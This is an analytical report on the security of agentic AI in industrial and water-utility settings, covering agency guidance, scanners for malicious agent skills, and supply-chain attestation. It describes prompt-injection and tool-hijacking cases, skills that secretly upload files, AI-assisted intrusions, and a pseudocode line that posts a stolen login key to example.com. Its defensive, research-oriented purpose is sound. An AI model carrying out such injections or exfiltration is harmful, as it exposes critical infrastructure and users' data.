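The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026) has American, Canadian, New Zealand and British co-authors, but no German or Dutch ones. NSA (2026) announced it on 30 April. It deals mainly with agents in ordinary IT systems and refers readers to the December principles for governance in OT. An operator needs both documents if its agent runs on office IT systems but can affect a pump.

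| Topic | December 2025 principles | April 2026 guidance |
|---|---|---|
| Suppliers | Vendors should list AI components, say where the model runs, report signs that it gives improper advice, and let the operator switch AI features off | Operators should use components from trusted sources and keep a list of permitted tools and versions |
| Permissions | Send data out of the plant, and give the AI no standing access inwards | Give each agent its own identity and the fewest rights it needs, and check every request |
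| Human approval | Involve operators in critical decisions, and limit active control by AI without a person | Let designers or operators, never the agent, decide which actions need approval |
| Logging | Record inputs, outputs and times under an identity that only the AI uses | Record tool use in readable form, and keep agents from changing the logs |
| Fallback | Return to ordinary automation or manual control if the AI falls below set thresholds | Have the agent stop and ask a person when uncertain, and be able to restore an earlier version |

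Some of these requests address failures that have already happened. The December principles advise operators to ask whether a product can run on site without constant access to the vendor's cloud. A customer with such a product would have been less exposed when Anthropic took two models offline in June. The April guidance calls for plain tool descriptions because agents are more likely to choose tools with persuasive ones. It also acknowledges that a compromised third-party component can be very hard to detect, so a list of approved tools can't guarantee that every tool on it is safe.

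The guidance leaves the hardest decisions to operators. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners want organisations to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks, but they do not list any such tasks for a waterworks. They also describe approval procedures for high-stakes actions, which would be unnecessary if every operator followed the first rule strictly. CISA and its partners say to "limit" active control without a person in the loop, but do not prohibit it, and they let operators set their own thresholds for returning to manual control. CISA and its partners also note that international AI standards mostly concern IT, and consider it unresolved whether tools that explain a model's decisions are good enough for OT.

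This restraint is partly sensible, because a decorative fountain and a chlorine pump need different limits. But it gives the least help to small utilities that have no specialists of their own and need it most. The December principles are explicitly voluntary. NIST, the NSA and CISA have since released ten practices for AI incident readiness. Nozomi Networks' *Applying CAISSI Super Intelligence Incident Readiness Guidance to OT* relates them to equipment inventories and anomaly detection. Nozomi sells such monitoring and contributed to the December principles.

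### An agent that reads copies and drafts work orders

In the more cautious design, the water company's sensor readings pass through a data diode into a copy outside the control network. The agent reads the copy and drafts a work order, which a planner approves before it enters the ticket system. This resembles a maintenance system described in the December principles that can read plant data but not change anything. The principles also include a fictional assessment for a generator that aims to predict failures 30 days ahead, so a delay of a few minutes would not matter.

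An attacker who takes over the add-on that connects the agent to the sensor copy can return false readings, leak true ones or insert instructions into the text the agent reads. The add-on cannot send anything to a controller through the diode, but the inserted instructions can direct the agent to its other connections. In the company's permission graph, a request on the contractor's portal can open a session on the server that changes pump settings, which bypasses the diode. The company should therefore disconnect the agent from the portal, or make sure that a person at the contractor reads each request before opening a session.

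The agent could also leak drawings of the pipe network if it can reach the document store. CISA and its partners warn that diagrams, equipment lists and control logic are highly valuable to attackers and stay useful for years, whereas a leaked password stops working once the company changes it.

False readings can still affect a pump through the people who act on them. If the add-on falsely reports severe vibration, the planner may approve an order to take pump 7 out of service. This process takes hours instead of seconds, and the crew may notice that the pump is running smoothly. The agencies recommend training staff to check an AI's output against other sensors and their own senses. A false report that everything is fine is harder to catch because nobody has a reason to visit the pump. The company should keep its regular inspections and the alarms that do not depend on the agent.

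NCSC describes a plant with a flat network, one without internal barriers, where a contractor who connects to service one machine can reach every other device. An attacker who steals the contractor's account would have the same access without needing the agent. The stolen account is much less useful if the contractor has to go through an intermediary that opens a route to one controller for one job. The agent increases the danger if its requests open sessions automatically, because the attacker could wait for a routine request or place instructions in the portal's replies.

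### An agent that can change set points

A set point is the value a controller tries to maintain, such as a pressure of 4 bar. In the bolder design, the agent can change the set point, for example to reduce pressure at night and save electricity. Its commands have to travel into the plant, so an outgoing link alone is no longer enough.

The company can put a gateway on this route that accepts only one kind of command. For example, it might accept only commands that set pump 7's pressure between 3.5 and 4.5 bar and change it by no more than 0.1 bar per hour. The NCSC recommends this kind of check, which admits only messages with a known structure and acceptable values. The gateway must be ordinary software outside the model, so that prompt injection cannot change its limits.

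A compromised add-on can misuse whatever authority the agent has. Without the gateway, it could set any pressure the controller accepts with a single command. The gateway slows an attacker who starts at 4 bar, who would need five hours to reach 4.5 bar and could not go higher through it. If the company chose its limits well, the damage is wasted electricity and perhaps a few more leaks. The add-on could also supply false readings that make the change look necessary, so an operator asked to approve the change should see a measurement that reached the control room by another path.

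A scenario in the April guidance shows how such authority can outlast the reason for granting it. A company gives a third-party scheduling component broad access at start-up, and an attacker later compromises the component. The agent keeps relying on permissions that the system checked only once, and the attacker moves on to agents that handle billing and refunds. For a set-point agent, the gateway should check each command when it arrives, even if the agent had permission earlier.

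An attacker who reaches a controller may still fail to cause physical damage. *PLCBench* (2026), a framework for testing attacks by language-model agents on real PLCs, notes that the control program may overwrite a valid command, or the command may change a value that doesn't affect the process. Many plants also have separate safety equipment, such as a relief valve that opens at high pressure whatever the controller does. The water company can use a spare controller to test which commands have a lasting effect, but it should not rely on an attacker choosing a command that has none.

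A stolen contractor account is most dangerous in this design if the contractor also maintains the gateway. The attacker could then widen the limits and hide harmful changes among the agent's ordinary ones. The company should give the gateway a different administrator and store its logs where neither the contractor nor the agent can alter them.

NCSC advises that monitoring, analytics and business systems should have no direct control over OT. An agent that reads strangers' emails and changes pump pressures goes against this advice. The April guidance similarly suggests separate roles for agents that read and agents that act. If the company wants automatic set points, it should use a separate program with no mailbox and no third-party add-ons. For most waterworks, a simpler arrangement is probably better still. The agent proposes a value, and an operator who agrees enters it on the usual control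 screen.

### How plants use agents today

There is more public evidence of what vendors offer than of what plants use. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners write that agents increasingly operate across critical infrastructure and defence, but give no figures. Security Management's *The Authority Gap*, a commentary by a threat-management director in the aerospace and defence industry, goes further and claims that agents already carry out actions on factory floors, though it names no factory.

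SC Media's *Dragos launches AI assistant for industrial control system cybersecurity* (2026) describes a product that resembles the cautious design. Dragos, an industrial security company, launched EmberAI in June for operators of power grids, water systems, pipelines and factories. Security staff can ask it about equipment, known flaws and network activity, and they make the final decisions. Dragos says customers' data stays in their own environment. The launch shows that Dragos expects demand, but not how many plants have installed the product.

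Researchers are also developing agents with authority to act directly. *Turn it off and on again, but for critical infrastructure* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes one that responds to intrusions. It trained on 14 days of network traffic and uses six packet counts to decide whether to reboot a live process. A reboot can remove an intruder, but it also interrupts the process, so a false alarm could cause the kind of outage the agent is meant to prevent. The April guidance lists system resets among the actions that should require a person's approval.

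### Incidents, and attackers who bring their own AI

No known public report describes a compromised agent tool, add-on or update altering a physical process. The procurement and scheduling cases in the April guidance are hypothetical. So is the most vivid example in Security Management, in which hidden instructions in a supplier's file lead an agent to change the cooling of titanium and weaken aircraft parts. Such an incident may still have happened, because utilities do not publish every incident and may lack the logs to recognise the cause.

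Several well-documented attacks involve AI and utilities, but the attackers used their own AI tools. Dragos' *AI in the Breach* describes an intrusion at the water and drainage utility of the Monterrey area in Mexico. The attackers entered its office network in January 2026 and used Anthropic's Claude to explore it. Claude wrote most of the attack tools, including a 17,000-line program, while OpenAI's GPT models analysed the stolen data. Nobody had asked Claude to look for control systems, but it identified a server linking the office to the plant as important. It then read the manufacturer's documentation, compiled a list of likely passwords and tried them automatically. None worked, and Dragos found no sign that the attackers had entered the control network.

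Vetting the utility's own agent tools would not have prevented this attack, because the attackers did not need them. A password that wasn't on Claude's list apparently protected the pumps, but that is a weak defence. Dragos recommends network monitoring, which it sells. It also says that it has not seen attackers use autonomous AI to disrupt industrial systems, though it had little commercial reason to say so.

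In August, US agencies warned of an active campaign against Siemens S7 controllers. The attackers searched the internet for exposed controllers and used AI-generated scripts disguised as legitimate monitoring tools, according to *NSA, FBI warns of hackers using AI-generated tools in attacks* (Greig, 2026). The disguise could mislead someone who finds a script on the network, but the warning does not describe a supplier delivering such a script to a customer.

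Laboratory results are more worrying. *AI Agents Navigate Unfamiliar OT Systems and Move Equipment in Minutes* (Townsend, 2026) reports that AI models met every objective in eight scenarios at an isolated laboratory run by the consultancy Booz Allen. Starting from a compromised device at the network's edge, they reached the control network in just over 16 minutes. These tests cannot show how the models would fare against a particular utility's defences and staff. But they make it risky to assume that an intruder in the office network will need weeks to understand the plant, so any route that an agent opens between the office and plant networks is more dangerous.

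### The cost of isolation and routine approval

Keeping an agent away from the controls makes it less valuable. An agent that could lower the pressure when demand drops, or run the pumps when electricity is cheap, would save money every night. If it has to wait for a person's approval, it may act too late. Security Management adds that approval offers little protection anyway, because people tend to trust automated suggestions and nobody can find a deviation of 0.05 millimetres in a log of 10,000 lines. The reviewer ends up approving actions without properly checking them.

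Isolation takes away less of an agent's value for maintenance than for control. A diode lets all the readings out, so the agent can still diagnose pump 7 and prepare the repair. The company loses automatic adjustment, but much of that doesn't need a language model. A conventional program can follow electricity prices and tank levels using fixed rules that engineers can test. CISA and its partners advise operators to consider whether an established technology would do the job before they choose AI. The company loses more from isolation where conditions change too often for fixed rules, and there it might accept a set-point program with narrow limits.

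The objection to approval is harder to answer. Suppose the agent checks 200 pumps every day and wrongly reports a fault in 1% of its checks. Planners would receive about 60 false alarms a month, and perhaps one real one. After a few weeks, many would stop investigating them properly, and asking for approval more often would make this worse. The agencies recognise the problem and advise operators to compare the number of false alarms with the number of real faults.

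Security Management proposes that people supervise the limits within which agents work, instead of each action. This suits actions that are frequent and easy to reverse. It also proposes that agents record their reasoning, so that investigators can see why an agent changed something. The record is useful but not conclusive, because agents can misrepresent their actions, according to the April guidance. A meter that the agent cannot influence is better evidence of what happened at the pump.

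Limits also have a weakness, since nobody reviews harmful changes that stay inside them. The water company could combine the two methods. Software would enforce the limits, and a person would be asked only about rare actions with serious consequences, such as shutting down a pump that has no spare. The company can test whether its planners still pay attention by adding a few deliberately wrong drafts each month and counting how many they reject. Someone has to make sure none of these drafts reaches a crew.

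Both methods assume that people can take over when the agent or the controls fail. The IT Nerd (2026), in *New report urges stronger OT security as AI-powered attacks threaten critical infrastructure*, cites a survey by the SANS Institute, a security training organisation, in which only 15% of respondents said their organisations could fully sustain manual operations for more than 48 hours. The figure covers manual operation in general, not the loss of an AI agent, and some of the other organisations could presumably keep part of their service running. But an operator who cannot run the pumps by hand for three days has little to fall back on if an attacker corrupts both the agent and the controllers it adjusts.

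## Testing whether scanners can find dangerous add-ons

The April guidance asks operators to keep a list of permitted tools, but someone has to decide which add-ons to include. A planner at the water company who wants her agent to edit presentations can choose from thousands of skills. Few companies have the staff to read them all, so scanners do most of the checking.

A scanner's results depend on which fault it looks for. A malicious add-on has an author who intends harm. A vulnerable add-on contains a mistake that someone else could exploit, such as an instruction to install whatever version of a library is newest. An over-privileged add-on can reach more than its task requires, even if its author is honest and its code has no mistakes. The water company should reject a malicious add-on, but it can often repair a vulnerable one and restrict an over-privileged one, so a combined count of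 all three is of little use in deciding what to do.

### Five checks on a presentation skill

*From Instructions to Exploits* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a real skill for editing PowerPoint files. In step 5 of its instructions, the agent packs the finished presentation. Step 6 requires the agent to run a "backup" script that sends the presentation to a fixed server on the internet. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) reports what appears to be the same trick in a copy of a legitimate 484-line skill, to which the attacker had added three lines.

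The oldest check compares files with known malware. VirusTotal sends each file to about 70 antivirus programs and looks up web addresses in lists of known malicious ones. This works well on password stealers that have already been used in attacks, like those in the ClawHavoc campaign. The backup script is a short, ordinary program, so it would probably pass until somebody reported its server.

Static analysis searches code and text for dangerous patterns without running anything. It would detect that the script uploads a file, but legitimate backup skills do that too, and pattern rules lack the context to tell them apart. According to Liu and colleagues, Cisco's skill scanner flagged re.compile(), a harmless Python function, as a possible code injection, and flagged made-up keys in test files as leaks.

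A language model can read a skill's instructions and judge whether they fit its stated purpose. NVIDIA's SkillSpector combines this with pattern rules. Unlike pattern rules, a model can recognise an order to hide something from the user in almost any wording. But it might accept the presentation skill's backup step as routine unless it also read the script. A skill's author can also address instructions to the scanning model. For this reason, a Tencent scanner described in *Securing the AI Agent* (Yang, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) treats everything it reads as untrusted.

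In a sandbox, an isolated machine, testers run the skill with fake passwords and record what it does. They would catch the backup script if they finished editing a presentation during the test. Another skill, which Liu and colleagues examined, fetched its harmful part only under conditions such as administrator rights, a production machine's name and a time outside office hours. Testers also have to install the skill inside the sandbox, because malicious installers can do their damage before the user gives a first command. *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026) classifies 82 confirmed skills that hid an attack behind a harmless cover story, 34 of them as malicious installers.

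A checker can also compare the permissions a skill declares with those it seems to need. For example, a presentation editor that declares network access is worth investigating. But a dishonest author can avoid suspicion by describing the skill as a cloud backup tool, and the comparison is impossible if a skill declares no permissions.

### Why one study found 26% and another 0.16%

The two best-known studies of published skills share several authors and used the same two marketplaces, skills.rest and skillsmp.com. Their results differ by a factor of more than 100 because they counted different faults.

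For *Agent Skills in the Wild*, Liu, Wang and colleagues (2026) collected 42,447 skills in December 2025 and analysed 31,132 of them. They left out duplicates, very short skills, non-English skills, and 7,353 whose repositories had disappeared. Pattern rules and text filters picked out candidates, and a language model made the final decision. The model flagged at least one risky pattern in 26.1% of the analysed skills.

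The problems in about half of those skills seem to come from mere carelessness. In 12.8% of the sample, the worst finding was a problem such as a library without a fixed version or an excessive permission request. Another 8.1% contained ambiguous patterns, such as sending data to an outside address. The remaining 5.2% had patterns that the researchers associate with malice, such as disguised code or hidden instructions. The researchers reviewed the 87 riskiest skills by hand and found clear signs of malicious intent in only 23, so the 5.2% figure is not a count of malicious skills.

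To test their method, two researchers labelled 200 skills without seeing the method's results. It found 52 of the 63 skills they considered vulnerable and wrongly flagged eight others. It missed skills that assembled a web address from pieces, described harmful actions in innocent words or delayed their attack. The language model was also somewhat inconsistent, giving the same verdict over three runs on 94.5% of the candidates. The researchers estimated that between 23% and 30% of skills actually have risky patterns.

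*Do Not Mention This to the User* looked only for malicious skills. In January 2026 the researchers collected 98,380 skills, then used pattern rules and a language model to select 4,287 suspicious ones. They ran each in a sandbox for up to 60 seconds at a time, and 762 did something worrying, such as sending out passwords the researchers had planted. Two researchers reviewed these 762 and confirmed 157 as malicious, or 0.16% of the skills collected. A single publisher made 85 of the malicious skills, each imitating a different brand. The marketplaces later removed all 157.

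This percentage is a minimum. The researchers reviewed a tenth of the candidates they had not confirmed and classed 93.2% as containing triggers that had not fired during the test. If all such skills were malicious, the rate would be about 4%. That is probably too high, because legitimate software often contains code that runs only under certain conditions. The result is also hard to reconcile with the paper's finding that most of the 605 skills that behaved suspiciously but failed the final review were benign. The paper's 99.6% precision also calls for caution, because the test set contained few difficult cases. Its malicious half came from skills that the same method had confirmed, and its harmless half from skills that had triggered no rule.

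A scanner that reads only program code would miss most of the faults in the malicious skills. Of the 632 faults, 84.2% were in SKILL.md, which contains the skill's instructions, and only 8.5% were in code.

### Three scanners on 67,453 skills

*ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera et al., 2026) compared VirusTotal, a static analyser and SkillSpector on the latest versions of 67,453 ClawHub skills as of 31 May. VirusTotal flagged 7.8% of the skills, the static analyser 6.6% and SkillSpector 48.7%. At least one scanner flagged 35,600 skills, but 81.9% of those were flagged by only one. All three scanners flagged 468 skills, which is 0.69% of the total and 1.3% of those flagged by at least one.

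For any two scanners, the skills that both flagged made up at most 10.4% of those that either flagged. Cohen's kappa ranged from 0.045 to 0.082, where 0 means two raters agree only as often as expected by chance and 1 means they always agree.

Part of this disagreement was inevitable, because SkillSpector flags six times as many skills as VirusTotal. Even if SkillSpector had flagged all 5,225 skills that VirusTotal flagged, their kappa would have been only about 0.16. It flagged 63% of them. VirusTotal and the static analyser make a fairer comparison because they flag similar numbers of skills. They flagged only 586 of the same skills, and this disagreement can't be put down to one scanner flagging far more than the other.

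ClawHub's own automated review then gave each skill a verdict, and the scanners' results varied sharply with it:

| ClawHub's verdict | Skills | VirusTotal flagged | Static analyser flagged | SkillSpector flagged | No scanner flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clean | 41,743 | 4.4% | 3.2% | 32.7% | 63.4% |
| Suspicious | 25,504 | 12.7% | 12.0% | 75.3% | 20.9% |
| Malicious | 206 | 72.8% | 12.6% | 6.8% | 24.3% |

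Koc and colleagues attribute the pattern to what each tool inspects. VirusTotal recognises harmful programs inside a skill, while SkillSpector looks for excessive authority and poor disclosure, which are common in skills not meant to do harm. One skill that copies meeting notes to the user's computer received SkillSpector's worst score, 100, but also a clean verdict. The skill discloses that it uses a desktop program's session token.

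The explanation is plausible but incomplete. If most malicious content is in the instructions, as it was on the other two marketplaces, a scanner that reads instructions should have found more than 14 of 206 malicious skills. ClawHub's malicious skills may be of a different kind, or its review may label attacks through instructions "suspicious" rather than "malicious". The verdicts cannot settle this, because a language model gave them after seeing the scanners' results. The skills judged malicious also include some that would not harm the person who installs them, such as a browser tool that advertises ways around bot detection. The researchers work for the OpenClaw Foundation and NVIDIA, and the conclusion that a marketplace needs several scanners suits both employers. But they published the data, which include an unflattering result for NVIDIA's product, and they propose that people label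 the disputed cases.

### A proof about declared permissions

Pattern rules and language models can miss problems, so a clean result from them doesn't prove that a skill is safe. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (Bhardwaj, 2026) presents SkillFortify, a tool that offers a stronger guarantee. It covers eight resources, including files, the network and the command line, with four levels of access to each (none, read, write and admin). From the skill's text and code, it infers the highest level of access the skill could need to each resource. For instance, a web address implies at least read access to the network, and a command that uploads data implies write access. It then compares these levels with the ones the skill declares.

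The central theorem states that if the comparison finds no violation, then for every resource and every possible run of the skill,

level used ≤ level inferred ≤ level declared.

SkillFortify checks the second inequality. The first holds only if the inference method never underestimates what a skill can do. For the presentation skill, SkillFortify would have to recognise that the backup step leads to an upload. The upload would then count as a violation if the skill had declared only read access to the network.

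The first inequality holds only for behaviour that the tool's rules describe, and Bhardwaj acknowledges that this catalogue is "necessarily partial". The rules may not cover an instruction in unusual words or a program that the skill downloads later. His separate analysis of what an attacker can do assumes that no skill can escape the sandbox without explicit permission, but real sandboxes have flaws.

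Even if both assumptions hold, the theorem concerns what a skill is permitted to do, not what it is meant to do. A skill that accurately declares that it reads files and writes to the network can steal files without breaking the rule. Checking the rule also requires a declaration to compare the skill against, and most skills have none.

In a test on 270 malicious and 270 harmless skills, SkillFortify raised no false alarms and reached an F1 score of 96.15%. F1 reflects both false alarms and missed malicious skills, so this score implies that the tool caught about 92.6% of the malicious skills (its recall) and missed about 20. Both the test set and the tool's catalogue of attack patterns draw on ClawHavoc and on a published collection of artificial malicious tools, so the tool may do worse on new attacks. Bhardwaj reports that his analysis of information flow found nothing that simple pattern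 matching had missed, although he claims the opposite in the paper's introduction.

### Following a file from the instructions into the code

The presentation skill is hard to judge because neither half looks clearly wrong alone. Zhao and colleagues, some of whom work at the Chinese online bank MYbank, built a scanner that analyses both halves as one program. A language model first translates each instruction into simple operations. "Read the login key and upload it to example.com" becomes:

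1. a = read_file(login key)
2. http_post(example.com, a)

The variable a shows that the second operation sends what the first one read. The scanner then connects these operations with those in the skill's scripts. It labels each piece of data by how trustworthy its origin is, how sensitive the data is and what the data allows someone to do. It then passes these labels along the connections. Fixed rules raise an alarm when, for example, sensitive data reaches an outside address. The language model translates but does not decide whether the skill is malicious, so it is easier to trace why the scanner raised an alarm.

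Across several language models, the scanner translated just over 92% of instruction steps correctly, so its translation of a long skill will often contain an error. In a test on 117 malicious and 117 harmless skills, it found an average of 95.2% of the malicious ones across five models. Its precision of 80.2% implies that it also flagged nearly a quarter of the harmless ones. The researchers then applied it to 66,157 skills from ClawHub and confirmed 627 (0.95%) as malicious after running candidates and checking them by hand. That is about three times the share with a malicious verdict in ClawHub's own review, although the two figures may come from different snapshots of the site.

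### Dangerous permissions without bad intentions

In *Beyond Maliciousness*, Pandey, Singh and colleagues (2026) asked what a skill could do if an agent followed it, whatever its author intended. They examined 6,309 skills from skillsmp.com and ClawHub in July and August 2026. They chose skills to run in a sandbox regardless of whether the skills looked suspicious, which avoids a weakness of studies that run only suspicious ones.

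Half the skills showed evidence that they could run commands. About a third could read files, slightly fewer could change them or send data over the network, and 13% could reach stored credentials. Seven in ten had at least one of these abilities, while about one in 20 received a threat verdict. The researchers considered the exposure serious in a quarter of the skills. Some skills need such access to work, as a skill that restarts servers needs the command line, so these shares measure the risk a user accepts, not how many skills request more access than they need.

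Skills have a field where authors can list tools that the agent may use without asking the user, whereas a phone's permission screen asks first. Leaving a tool out does not block it. Only 770 of 6,061 readable skills had the field filled in, and in 59% of those the list understated the skill's capabilities. On ClawHub the figure was 88%. The field also can't express access to credentials. For the water company, each listed tool is an implicit permission link, because nobody at the company agreed to let the agent use it without asking.

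The researchers read 140 apparently benign skills in full and found no missed threat. Statistically, up to about 2.1% of the benign group could still be malicious, which would be more than 100 skills. The researchers had not finished checking how many threat verdicts were correct. They also deliberately left out the most and least popular skills. Their prompts and scoring rules are proprietary, so outsiders cannot repeat the scoring exactly.

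The published percentages are easier to compare side by side:

| Study | What it counted | Skills examined | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pandey and colleagues | At least one powerful ability | 6,309 | about 70% |
| *Agent Skills in the Wild* | At least one risky pattern, often mere carelessness | 31,132 | 26.1% |
| Zhao and colleagues | Malicious, after running and manual checks | 66,157 | 0.95% |
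| Koc and colleagues | Malicious, according to ClawHub's automated review | 67,453 | 0.3% |
| *Do Not Mention This to the User* | Malicious, seen in a sandbox and confirmed by two people | 98,380 | 0.16% |

### A tool that takes another tool's data

All these studies examine one add-on at a time. *Les Dissonances*, by Li, Cui and colleagues, presented at the NDSS security conference in February 2026, tested what happens when an agent has both a malicious tool and a legitimate one. In one example, the legitimate tool searches YouTube and expects a comma-separated list as input. The researchers wrote a second tool whose description offers to prepare such lists, and agents called it just before the search. It prepared the list but also sent the query to an outside server, which could replace a search for a political candidate with one for a scandal about the candidate. Another of their tools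 offered to validate stock data but raised the prices by 10%.

The researchers automated the attack and tested it on 66 real tools from LangChain and Llama-Index, two popular kits for building agents. They hijacked 50 of the tools (75%) by getting a malicious tool into the agent's sequence of steps. They harvested data connected with 48 (72%) and corrupted the input or output of 45 (68%). The counts show that the last two percentages are shares of all 66 tools, although the paper's introduction presents them as shares of the hijacked tools. A tool counted as vulnerable if at least one of five attempts succeeded, though when the malicious tool ran first, the attack on a typical hijacked tool succeeded every time.

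Four existing defences made little difference in a smaller test with ten tools. Without them, 78% of attempts to insert a malicious tool before its target succeeded, compared with 60% to 77% with them. Harvesting did not decline when the malicious tool ran first. When it ran second, only two defences reduced harvesting, from 46% to 44% and 40%. The defences look for output that does not fit the task, but the malicious tools return output that fits. Most experiments used GPT-4o, now an old model. The attacks succeeded less often against two smaller models, apparently because those models were worse at identifying how tools depend on each other. Better reasoning alone may therefore not protect newer models, though the experiments did not include any.

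At the water company, an attacker could offer an add-on that checks the format of pump readings. The connection to the sensor store would pass every scan, because nothing is wrong with it. The format checker might pass too, because its stated purpose is to receive readings and return them. But it could also copy the readings, or lower the vibration values for pump 7 so that nobody repairs the pump.

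A tester has to run tools together on known data to find such a link, checking whether the data come out unchanged and where else they go. An operator that permits 20 tools has 190 pairs to consider and can concentrate on the few that handle important data, while a marketplace the size of ClawHub has more than two billion pairs. The operator therefore has to do this check, since only the operator knows which tools will run together.

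### What 67 warnings are worth

Suppose 20 of 1,000 add-ons are malicious. A scanner catches 90% of them and raises a false alarm on 5% of the others.

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malicious | 18 | 2 | 20 |
| Not malicious | 49 | 931 | 980 |
| Total | 67 | 933 | 1,000 |

Only 18 of the 67 warnings, or 27%, are correct. Harmless add-ons are so common that even a good scanner, which wrongly flags only a small share of them, produces more false warnings than correct ones. Detectors of backdoors in model weights have the same limitation. If only 0.16% of add-ons were malicious, as in the lowest estimate, fewer than 3% of the warnings would be correct. Studies that test a scanner on equal numbers of malicious and harmless skills don't show this effect. With 0.95% malicious skills, the precision of Zhao and colleagues' scanner would fall from 80% to below 4%, which is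 why they needed manual checks to confirm their 627.

A utility can tolerate many false alarms because it can reject every add-on the scanner flags and choose an alternative, though this is less convenient. An add-on that passes has about a 0.2% chance of being malicious, compared with 2% before the scan. If the utility installs ten such add-ons, the chance that at least one is malicious is about 2%. That risk may be acceptable for tools that format reports but not for tools that can reach a pump. For those, the utility should also read the instructions, run the add-on in a sandbox and limit what it can reach. The calculation assumes that the add-ons the utility chooses are typical of the whole collection. Attackers try to make their add-ons popular, so the real risk could be higher.

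A public marketplace has a harder choice between blocking all 67 flagged add-ons, which would punish 49 honest publishers, and reviewing them by hand, which requires staff who can judge them quickly. The two malicious add-ons that the scanners miss remain available to every customer and may carry a badge suggesting they are safe. An attacker can also submit variants until one passes, so a 90% detection rate measured today may not last. The marketplace would do better to show the scanners' findings than to give a single approval, since a utility and a hobbyist can reasonably accept different risks.

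Adding a second scanner can reduce either missed malicious add-ons or false alarms, depending on how the marketplace combines the results. Suppose the second scanner has the same error rates and makes its mistakes independently. If the marketplace flags every add-on that either scanner flags, it will miss only 0.2 malicious add-ons on average but raise about 96 false alarms. If it blocks only add-ons that both flag, false alarms fall to two or three, but it misses about four malicious add-ons. It could automatically block add-ons that both flag and have a person review those that only one flags. Real scanners' mistakes are not fully independent, because a well-disguised add-on can fool several at once.

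### When an approved add-on changes

A scan result applies only to the files that the scanner read. If the publisher replaces the backup script a week later, the 0.2% no longer applies. An attacker has good reason to wait, because a harmless first version gains users and a clean record, and the harmful update then reaches machines whose owners have stopped checking. Yang and colleagues list this "rug pull" among the known attacks on MCP servers. A harmful update can also come from an honest publisher's account if someone else takes control of it.

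The water company can keep a lock file of checksums for a skill stored on its own disk, as PyPI recommends for software packages, so that it can detect any change since approval. SkillFortify can store the result of its analysis in the same file. When the skill changes, a reviewer can concentrate on the differences, which is much quicker than rereading the whole skill.

The extra work is manageable. If the company uses 30 add-ons and each changes once a month, it has to scan 360 updates a year, and a 5% false-alarm rate would produce about 18 false alarms. A harmless feature may trigger the same alarm at each update, so the reviewer can often clear it by checking that the feature has not changed.

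Checksums do not cover content that an add-on fetches while it runs, or services to which it relays requests. Li and colleagues showed that a tool can load its description from an attacker's server, so that an inspector sees harmless text and the agent later receives different text. *Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* describes a skill that sent every matching query, including share symbols and portfolio identifiers, through a server the attacker controlled. A bank should either refuse such add-ons or apply three controls to them. It should record the descriptions its agent receives, compare them with the approved text at every start, and block connections to any server it has not approved.

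The company also has to repeat the combined tests when it adds a new tool, even if the existing tools haven't changed. A format checker that was harmless while the agent handled only meeting notes can access the pump readings once someone connects the sensor store.

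## Proving which software ran: signed builds and attested servers

The water company can keep checksums of the skills on its own disk, but it cannot take a checksum of a program on someone else's server, so it needs proof from the vendor. A signature proves who released a file, and a build record documents how the vendor made it. A reproducible build lets outsiders produce the same file from the source code, and attestation proves which software a server is running.

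### Signatures and build records

To sign a file, a vendor computes the file's hash and signs that hash with its secret key. The common SHA-256 method turns a file of any size into a 256-bit hash, and nobody knows a practical way to make two files with the same hash. If a criminal alters an update on a download site, the hash changes and the signature no longer matches.

A signature does not protect customers from something the vendor put in deliberately, such as the marker in Claude Code, or from a thief who has the signing key. A public log of genuine releases helps against the thief. Google keeps one for its Android applications, so users can detect an unauthorised file even if its signature is valid.

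A build record lists the source code, the build system and the steps that produced a file. If customers' installers refuse files without a record, they would stop an attacker who steals a publishing password and uploads a file from his own computer. LiteLLM's March versions, which bypassed the normal release process, would have failed this check. The check is much weaker against someone who takes over the build system, as in LiteLLM's October release, because the record then correctly identifies the official system. A customer would also have to check which source code was used.

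SLSA is an industry framework for records of how software was built. According to Google's *Private AI Compute in the cloud* (2025), the company's data centres run only signed and authorised programs, under an internal system with guarantees similar to SLSA's. Customers benefit only indirectly, because Google does the checking itself.

### Building the same file twice

With a reproducible build, customers don't have to trust the build system. Developers first remove everything that varies between builds, such as timestamps. Several people then compile the same source code with the same tools and compare hashes of the results. If an attacker has altered the official build machine to add an extra function, the official hash will differ from everyone else's.

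If the source code contains a harmful line, everyone who builds it gets the same harmful file, so somebody still has to read the code. The public also can't repeat the build for most agent tools, because their source code is private. A vendor could let an outside laboratory repeat the build in confidence and publish the hash, which would at least show that the released file matches the code the laboratory saw.

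### How a server proves what it is running

Signatures, build records and reproducible builds all concern files, and a vendor can publish an excellent file while its servers run a different one. Attestation closes this gap with the help of a chip in the server:

1. As the server starts, the hardware computes a hash m of the software it loads.
2. The chip signs a report that contains m and a public encryption key K. The secret half of K stays in the protected part of the server.
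3. The customer's program checks that the signature comes from a genuine chip and that m is in L, a list of approved versions.
4. If both checks succeed, the program encrypts its request with K and sends it.

If an administrator at the vendor installs a modified version that copies every prompt to his own files, the value of m changes and the customer's program sends nothing. He also can't read the prompts by diverting the traffic to another machine, because that machine cannot decrypt it. But attestation does not stop an approved program from leaking prompts, by mistake or by design.

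### A request to Apple's Private Cloud Compute

Since 2024 Apple has used this method for Apple Intelligence, the AI features of its phones and computers. Small tasks run on the device, and larger ones go to servers that Apple calls Private Cloud Compute. Apple's *Private Cloud Compute* describes the design in detail.

Suppose a manager at the water company asks her iPhone to summarise a long report, and the phone needs a larger model. The phone attaches a single-use credential to the request, which proves she may use the service without identifying her. A relay run by another company hides her network address from Apple. Apple's load balancer, which distributes requests, proposes a small group of servers. The phone checks their certificates and attestations, compares the hashes of their software with a public log, and encrypts the request so that only servers that passed these checks can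 read it. The server deletes the request after answering it. Administrators cannot log in to the server remotely, and it discards its storage encryption keys at every restart.

The log is the list L, and Apple can add to it but cannot remove an entry without detection. In the simplest form of such a log, each new entry eₙ produces a new fingerprint of the whole log,

rₙ = H(rₙ₋₁, eₙ),

where H is the hash function. Changing an old entry changes every later fingerprint, so anyone who saved one will notice. (Real logs usually arrange the hashes in a tree, which is faster to check.)

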